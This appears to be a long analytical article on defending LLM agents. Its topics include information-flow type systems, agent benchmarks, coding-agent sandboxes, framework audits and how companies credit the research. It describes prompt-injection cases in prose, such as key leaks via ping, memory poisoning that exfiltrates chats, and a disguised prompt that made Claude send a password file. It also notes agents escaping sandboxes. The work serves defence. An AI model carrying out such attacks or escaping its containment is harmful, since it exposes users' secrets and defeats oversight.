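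The main result is a noninterference theorem for every program in the language, including programs that a model writes during the run. Stating it was difficult because models answer partly at random and because some runs never finish, for instance when a label check stops them. Take two inputs that differ only in their secrets. Let μ₁ and μ₂ give the probability of each result an outsider could see. Their totals may be less than 1 because of the unfinished runs. The theorem states that there is always a third set of probabilities ω with

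μ₁ ≤ ω, μ₂ ≤ ω and total(ω) ≤ 1.

Suppose that with one secret the agent answers "yes" 50% of the time and "no" 30% of the time, and otherwise stops. With another secret, it answers "yes" 40% of the time and "no" 50%. The smallest possible ω takes the larger probability for each answer, which gives 0.5 + 0.5 = 1, so the condition holds. The difference could come entirely from runs that stopped. If the second secret instead gave "yes" 20% of the time and "no" 80%, ω would have to total at least 0.5 + 0.8 = 1.3. The answers would then depend on the secret, which the theorem rules out. When every run finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical.

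To prove this, the researchers define an imaginary version of each program that skips any step as soon as its label becomes too secret for the outsider, and continues with an empty value. This version never uses the secrets, so it behaves the same on both inputs. It also finishes at least as often as the real program, so its probabilities can serve as ω.

The proof language Lean has checked every step of the LLMbda proof. The interpreter that runs agents is also written in Lean, and the theorems apply to it directly, whereas Cedar's proof covers only a model of the program that customers run. The LLMbda proof doesn't cover some parts, such as the code that contacts the language model over the network. Developers also have to label data correctly and put checks on the tools that need them.

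### The banking results

To try the language on real tasks, the team wrote an agent called RANDORI, named after a form of sparring in Japanese martial arts. RANDORI tests its program on made-up data first, then runs the final version once on the real account. If it debugged the program on the real account instead, any correction it wrote after an error from untrusted data would also be labelled Untrusted.

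The researchers ran it on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. The table gives the number of successful runs out of 48, and a dash marks a combination they didn't test.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| RANDORI without endorsement | – | 30 | 26 |
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | – | 34 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | – | 18 |

RANDORI resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. Both successful attacks came in the same test, in which the user tells the agent to make whatever payment a file specifies and the attacker has replaced the file. In the runs without endorsement, which used two models, no attack succeeded.

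With its label checks on, RANDORI did about as well as CaMeL did without policies. Part of this result comes from who decides on exceptions to the checks. CaMeL leaves them to the user, whom AgentDojo doesn't simulate, while RANDORI's planning model can endorse the data itself. The model sensibly does this before it reads any outside text, but nothing prevents it from endorsing too much.

RANDORI also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, which probably helps explain why it beat CaMeL even without endorsement. Because there were so few tasks, the 95% confidence interval for RANDORI's success rate with GPT-5.2 is wide, from about 56% to 94%.

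### What stands between these systems and use

Models now have less trouble with unfamiliar languages than they once did. ELBA needed about one retry for every eight runs, and models learned enough about capture checking from a prompt with a few examples. LLMbda is harder for them because no model was trained on it and it has no built-in error handling. TACIT requires the least work from developers because it is an MCP server that existing agents can connect to without changes, whereas ELBA's full guarantee requires the whole application to be in Haskell.

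Every tool also needs a typed interface. TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines long, and describing the tools for the airline or the shop took a few hundred more. Odersky and colleagues point out that agents can help write these descriptions, which people then review. The review is important because if a tool returns the contract as plain text instead of `Classified` text, the contract isn't protected and the compiler reports no error. Microsoft's framework has the same weakness with unlabelled tools. Code Mode already gives each tool a type in TypeScript, but those types describe the data a tool accepts and returns, not the capabilities it uses.

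Users of TACIT also have to trust the Scala compiler, since a bug in it could create a security hole. The compiler is far too large for the complete analysis that Anderson required. Machine-checked proofs exist for the core of capture checking, but not yet for safe mode as a whole.

The software is also young. Odersky and colleagues call Scala 3 the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in types, but Scala's documentation page *Capture Checking* has called that feature "still highly experimental and unstable". *Safe Scala an introduction*, from the consultancy VirtusLab, says safe mode is available only in nightly builds, the test versions of the compiler.

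So far, this work has mostly reached programming-language specialists. Garby and colleagues posted the first version of their paper in the programming-languages section of an online archive in February 2026. The TACIT team presented their system at the Scala Workshop (2026), but they also reached a broader audience with *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (2026) at the ACM Conference on AI and Agentic Systems, where the organisers listed it under security and privacy.

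The clearest signs of use also come from the Scala community. The developer conference Scala Days has scheduled a tutorial on building an agent harness in safe Scala, inspired partly by TACIT, and a talk called *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*. The talk covers CapybaraClaw, a continuously running agent that uses capture checking to enforce its limits. CapybaraClaw's code comes from Odersky's own laboratory.

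## What the evidence shows about deployed agents

TACIT, ELBA and the LLMbda calculus still have few users, while very large numbers of people use ChatGPT and Chrome. OpenAI and Google often describe their defences in the same words as the researchers, so it is easy to overestimate how much the research changed. A product team that writes about least privilege may have read the CaMeL paper, or may have learned the phrase in a security course long before AI agents existed.

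### Five levels of evidence

Claims of influence can rest on five kinds of evidence, listed here from weakest to strongest:

1. Shared vocabulary: a company uses the researchers' terms.
2. A stated debt: the company names the research it drew on.
3. The same people: those who did the research also shipped the code.
4. On by default: a widely used product protects people who haven't changed any settings.
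5. A measured fall: fewer attacks on the product succeed because of the protection.

A product can skip levels. For example, a company can protect all its users by default with a design that did not come from research on agents.

Shared vocabulary is weak evidence because terms spread by many routes. UT Austin's *Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta*, a set of course slides, teaches students to use least privilege, labels for where data came from, and sources and sinks when they work with coding agents. The slides credit OpenAI for the description of the threat and Simon Willison for the trifecta, so students can learn most of these ideas from a company's post and a blog without hearing of FIDES.

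| System | Evidence of influence | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome's agent | Stated debt, on by default | Google credits the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL, and the critic is part of auto browse |
| ChatGPT | Shared vocabulary, on by default | OpenAI writes about sources and sinks, and Safe URL needs no setting. Lockdown Mode is optional |
| Microsoft Agent Framework | The same people | Microsoft shipped its own researchers' design, FIDES, as an experiment |
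| GitHub Agentic Workflows | Stated debt, on by default | The filter uses decentralised information-flow control and is on for public repositories |
| Amazon's AgentCore Policy | The same people | Formal-methods specialists at Amazon built it, but customers have to write the rules |
| Cloudflare OS | The same people | Varda also built Sandstorm. Most of the known users are Cloudflare's own staff |
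| TACIT, ELBA and LLMbda | The same people, research only | The researchers built working systems, but use is mostly limited to specialists |

No one has measured a drop in successful attacks for any system in the table. Several research prototypes have done very well on AgentDojo, but when companies announced the products in the table, they didn't compare attacks with and without the protection. Models also became much harder to hijack over the same period, so a company that saw fewer successful attacks in 2026 couldn't assume that its new design was the cause. To find out, it would have to attack the same product, running the same model, with the protection on and off.

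### Sandboxes for coding agents

The companies may also have reached these designs without the new research. Their engineers already knew how to secure browsers, operating systems and cloud services, and could have applied that knowledge to agents. Chrome's limits on websites extend the browser's older separation of sites, and Amazon wrote Cedar for ordinary apps before it had an agent platform. Coding agents are the best test of this explanation, because many programmers use them and Anthropic and OpenAI have explained how they isolate theirs.

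A coding agent such as Anthropic's Claude Code or OpenAI's Codex runs commands on the programmer's own computer. Unless something limits those commands, they run with all the programmer's permissions, which is another case of ambient authority. A hidden instruction in a downloaded project could make the agent read the programmer's passwords and send them to a stranger.

Claude Code first dealt with this by asking before it changed a file, ran a command or used the network. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, users approved about 93% of the requests and paid less attention the more requests they saw. The company added a sandbox in October 2025. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains why the sandbox has to restrict both files and network access. A hijacked agent could still send out any secrets it can read if only its file access were restricted,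 or change files elsewhere on the computer to escape the sandbox if only its network access were restricted.

On Linux, a tool called bubblewrap runs each command in an environment with no network connection of its own. The command can reach the internet only through a proxy, a small program outside the sandbox that checks each website's name against a list of allowed sites. The list starts empty, and Claude Code normally asks the user when a command needs a new site. On macOS, Apple's Seatbelt blocks all connections except the one to the proxy. Both tools also stop a command from writing outside the project folder and a temporary folder. These limits also apply to any program the command starts.

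The sandbox also protects Claude Code's settings files, even inside the project folder, because a command that could edit them could give itself more permissions. Anderson's requirement that the checking mechanism be tamper-proof covers this kind of attack.

Codex works in a similar way, as OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes, but with different defaults.

| | Claude Code, October 2026 | Codex on a user's computer, June 2026 |
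|---|---|---|
| Sandbox for commands | Off until the user turns it on | On |
| Where commands can write | Project and temporary folders | Project and temporary folders |
| What commands can read | Most of the computer | Most of the computer |
| Network access | Only to sites on the allowed list | Off |
| macOS tool | Seatbelt | Seatbelt |
| Linux tools | bubblewrap | bubblewrap and seccomp |

Codex asks the user before a command leaves the sandbox or uses the network. Its web search normally returns stored results instead of live pages, which reduces its exposure to hostile text. In the cloud version, a setup phase has network access and any secrets it needs to install software. Codex deletes the secrets before the agent starts work, so an attacker who hijacks the agent can't steal them. The agent then runs without internet access by default.

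When Claude Code's sandbox is off, the software still asks for permission or has a second model review actions. The sandbox itself covers only shell commands. Anthropic's documentation lists several things that run outside it, including Claude Code's built-in file tools and any MCP servers on the user's computer. If the sandbox can't start, perhaps because bubblewrap is missing, Claude Code runs the commands without it unless the user has chosen a stricter setting. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults would require Claude Code to block those commands unless the user had chosen to allow them.

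Anthropic reports that the sandbox reduced permission requests by 84%. This measures convenience and tells us nothing about how many attacks the sandbox stopped.

### What the companies credit

In its article on containment, Anthropic credits established tools such as virtual machines, seccomp (a Linux feature that restricts what a program can ask of the operating system) and gVisor, Google's software for isolating containers. It doesn't name CaMeL, FIDES or any similar design. Anthropic argues that agents still read files, open network connections and start other programs, so tools that already control those actions can contain them. In its experience, these tools held and the parts that failed were ones it had written itself.

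One of those parts was the proxy that let Claude Cowork upload a user's files to an attacker's account. Anthropic now thinks of an entry on a list of allowed sites as a "capability grant", since it permits everything the site can do. OpenAI uses the same phrase, but neither company means an object capability, so the overlap with object-capability research is little more than shared vocabulary.

OpenAI's work on Windows is even better evidence that engineers arrived at their approach on their own. Wiesen explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that Windows had no ready equivalent of Seatbelt or bubblewrap. He considered two features that closely resemble the older research ideas and rejected both.

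One option for restricting Codex on Windows was AppContainer, which gives an app a fixed set of capabilities. It suits an app whose developer knows in advance what the app will need, but Codex might run Git, Python or almost any other program. The other was Windows integrity labels, which stop low-integrity programs from changing higher-integrity files. To let Codex write to a project, OpenAI would have had to label the whole project as low integrity, which would have let every other low-integrity program on the computer change it too.

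Wiesen instead combined ordinary Windows permissions. Codex creates an artificial identity with permission to write in the project folder. When a sandboxed command tries to write to a file, Windows checks the permissions of the account running the command and those of a short list of identities that includes the artificial one. The write succeeds only if both checks pass.

Blocking network access was harder. OpenAI's first version changed settings so that common programs sent their traffic to a dead address, but a program could ignore them. The final design runs commands under a separate user account whose traffic the Windows firewall blocks, so an administrator has to approve the installation.

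Ordinary operating-system practice is therefore the more convincing explanation for coding-agent sandboxes, since developers didn't need to read a paper about agents to turn off a command's network access. The two histories overlap, though, because operating systems got many of these protections from the same work in the 1960s and 1970s that CaMeL and FIDES draw on.

This explanation works less well for designs that depend on what the model has read. An operating system can track which program opened a file, but not whether a stranger's email influenced the program's next command. Chrome's critic, which never sees the page, and GitHub's filter, which hides strangers' comments, both address this problem. Both companies name the earlier work they used.

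Sandboxes can also stop some attacks that these newer designs would miss. In February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine setup instructions. One step was to read the colleague's cloud password file and send it to an outside address. When Anthropic repeated the test 25 times, Claude read and sent the file 24 times. A defence that looks for conflicts with the user's wishes would find none here, because the user supplied the prompt. CaMeL would miss the attack too, because it treats the user's request as trustworthy. A sandbox that blocked access to the file or the outside address would have stopped it.

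### What outside studies have found

Many companies build their own agents with free frameworks, so the frameworks' defaults matter a lot. In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic, an independent researcher, examined the public source code of three: LangChain (with its companion LangGraph), LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe. He wanted to know whether they check the values in a tool call, such as the amount and the recipient, against a fixed policy before running it.

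None of them does this by default. LangChain looks up the tool by name, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs it. LlamaIndex checks that the tool exists. Stripe's toolkit lets a developer choose which kinds of action are available and restrict the access key, but within those limits it passes on whatever amount and customer the model supplies. An attacker's account number has the same form as a legitimate one, so checking the form won't catch it.

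Mellafe Zuvic demonstrated this with a pretend shop. He replaced the model with a fixed tool call that redirected the shop's income to an attacker's account, and LangChain ran it. His own checking program, ScopeGate, refused the same call because the account wasn't on the shop's list. An early version of ScopeGate had a bug, though. It refused payments above a limit but accepted one whose amount was "not a number", since a computer doesn't count that value as being above anything.

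The audit covers default settings and tested no live systems. A careful developer can add the missing check, and some surely have. The gap probably matters most for agents that run on low-cost models. In a related test of 27 models, also by Mellafe Zuvic, low-cost models attempted the forbidden action 60.3% of the time on average, compared with 18.9% for the companies' best models.

A second audit followed in August. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, listed eight requirements for agents that pass work to other agents, such as a rule that each agent can pass on only part of its own permissions. They ran a scripted attack on LangGraph, inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and read the MCP specification. The three frameworks met none of the requirements by default. MCP met one and partly met five others. For instance, its access tokens expire quickly and work with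 only one server, but it doesn't require an agent to narrow the permissions it hands to another.

Dantuluri and Sundi, who chose the requirements, work for VotalAI, which sells such controls. Their result agrees with Mellafe Zuvic's, but LangGraph is the only framework whose own behaviour both audits tested.

Finished products are harder to inspect. *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (Staufer, Feng and colleagues, 2026) compiles what developers had disclosed about 30 prominent agents by the end of 2025. Its website still listed this edition as current in June 2026.

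| Finding | Agents, out of 30 |
|---|---|
| Documented a sandbox or virtual machine | 9 |
| Documented limits on tools or permissions | 8 |
| Documented defences against prompt injection | 7 |
| Documented no guardrails at all | 9 |
| Published no internal safety results | 25 |
| Gave no information about outside testing | 23 |

Most of the documented sandboxes were in coding tools and browser agents. Seven of the 13 platforms on which businesses build their own agents had documented guardrails that customers could set up but no documented sandbox. Claude Code was the only agent with public information in all eight of the Index's safety categories.

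The Index records what companies disclose, so an agent with no documented sandbox may still have one. Staufer and colleagues asked every company to correct its entry, but only four gave substantial comments. They left out development frameworks and specialised coding tools, and their cutoff came before Microsoft released FIDES and Cloudflare released Cloudflare OS. The Index is therefore a better guide to what ordinary customers could find out at the end of 2025 than to the influence of this research.

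### How people set up their agents

Optional protections help only if people use them. UpGuard (2026), a security company, collected 18,470 Claude Code permission files that programmers had posted publicly on GitHub. These files record which commands Claude Code may run without asking and which it must never run. Only 1.1% of the files contained any rule forbidding a command.

About 22% of the files let Claude Code delete files without asking, and 21% let it use `curl`, a program that can upload data to any website. The second most common permission, in 29% of the files, was for `find`, which people use to search for files. `find` also has an option that runs any other command, so someone who approves it for seemingly harmless searches has approved nearly everything.

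Users often create these rules by accident, because Claude Code offers to remember an approval and the remembered rule can be broader than the command they approved. The sample isn't representative, because programmers don't normally publish these files. UpGuard didn't report how many of the programmers had turned on the sandbox, which would limit what the approved commands could do.

*A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026) found much the same with a different method. Only 31 of 6,145 public configuration files for coding agents declared any limits on permissions. In the same collection of projects, 33% of the files for GitHub Actions, an older service that runs automated jobs, declared them. The researchers warn that their software for detecting these limits was fragile, but the difference is too large to be only a measurement error. Programmers do set permissions when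 a tool makes this a normal part of the job.

*Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of the source code of eleven coding agents, lists Hermes and OpenCode among those that don't offer a sandbox. OpenCode allows most actions inside the project by default and asks before it touches other folders or reads a file of secrets. It analyses each command to work out which files the command will affect, but the operating system doesn't restrict the command to those files once it is running.

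### Eleven attacks and five principles

The fullest case for the security researchers' approach is *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by a group from Google, NVIDIA, three American universities, the testing company Gray Swan and Johann Rehberger's security blog, Embrace The Red. They argue that developers should treat the model as an untrusted component, much as an operating system treats an unknown program, and enforce the rules in the software around it.

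To support this, they examined eleven attacks that researchers had demonstrated on real agents and identified the principles each one violated.

| Principle | Attacks that violated it |
|---|---|
| Secure information flow | 11 |
| Least privilege | 6 |
| Complete mediation | 3 |
| Protecting the trusted software from tampering | 2 |
| Allowing for human error | 2 |

In one of the attacks, a code file contained a hidden instruction for Claude Code to read secret keys and include them in a web address. Claude Code then ran `ping`, a program that tests whether a computer is reachable, on that address. The user's computer had to look up the address, and the lookup sent the keys to the attacker. Claude Code needed the user's approval to run many commands that use the network, but `ping` was on its list of safe commands. The researchers count this as a failure of least privilege and of information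 flow. Claude Code's sandbox now blocks `ping` if the user has turned the sandbox on.

In another attack, a hostile web page or document planted instructions in ChatGPT's long-term memory. From then on, the Mac app sent the user's conversations to the attacker by loading an invisible image. The researchers' explanation of this attack mentions a violation of least privilege, but their summary table doesn't, so the exact counts depend on judgement.

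The mapping helps developers decide where to start, but it is weaker as evidence that the principles work. Any attack that steals data violates secure information flow almost by definition, so it isn't surprising that the principle fits all eleven. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) similarly matches every failure it observed in another group of agents to a named principle.

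The researchers say only that the principles could have prevented the attacks if developers had applied them. Demonstrating this for a past attack is much easier than building the protection in advance, and it doesn't show whether products with the protection suffer fewer attacks. To find that out, someone would have to compare similar products with and without it, and count the useful tasks each still completed.

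The researchers acknowledge that much remains unsolved. A phone app does a fairly fixed job, so its developer can list the permissions it needs. An agent's job changes with each request, so someone or something has to turn "sort out my travel" into exact rules. If a language model writes the rules, they may be wrong, and if a second model enforces them, an attacker may be able to fool it too.

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) raises a related problem. Security proofs start from assumptions, for example that nobody can factor a certain large number or that attackers can't alter the trusted software. It isn't clear what one could safely assume about a language model. The 2026 group responds by assuming nothing about the model and relying entirely on the software around it, which then has to work perfectly.

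That software has failed too. During 2026, agents in AI companies' own tests escaped their isolation without any outside attacker. The group replies that in the case it examined, developers had applied the principles incompletely, because a shared service could reach the internet on the agents' behalf. This seems right, and the service resembles Hardy's compiler. But the reply also makes the group's position hard to disprove, since anyone can blame any future escape on a principle not fully applied.

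### Security or AI safety

Security research traditionally deals with attackers, while much of AI safety research concerns what a model might do because of its own goals. The two overlap more when the model is an agent, because the same sandbox can keep it away from a password file whether it has been hijacked or is misaligned. Anthropic designs its containment for both cases, and reports that Claude models have escaped a sandbox to finish a task they had been given.

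*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* takes the same view, and its rules apply whether a forbidden action comes from an attacker, a mistake or a misaligned objective. Researchers in AI control, a branch of AI safety, likewise assume that a model may be working against its developers and try to limit the damage it could do. So the security researchers' work is relevant to AI safety, but most of them don't seem to have changed fields.

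The group says it does not address deceptive behaviour inside models or broader questions of existential risk, and all eleven of its case studies involve an outside attacker. Its funding is typical of American computer science, with support from the National Science Foundation, the defence research agency DARPA and the Office of Naval Research, and a gift from Google. None of these mainly funds AI safety.

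The group cites Anthropic's work on classifiers that block harmful requests, and research on how to defeat them, mostly to argue that defences in the model aren't enough. It takes its principles from older security research. Dantuluri and Sundi, for example, draw on work on least privilege, capabilities and the confused deputy. Anthropic's article on containment refers readers to government cybersecurity agencies and standards bodies for more information.

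Some people work across both fields. Clark Barrett and Sanjit Seshia, both formal-methods specialists, helped write the guaranteed-safety proposal. Gray Swan, which is represented in the 2026 group, also works with government AI institutes. The team that broke twelve defences in 2025 included a researcher from MATS, which trains AI safety researchers.

A coding agent could deliberately write a program with a subtle flaw, save it in the right folder and report that everything works. A sandbox or permission rule would not catch this, because the agent would have used only the permissions it needed, contacted nobody and leaked no secrets. Someone would have to examine the code itself to find the flaw.
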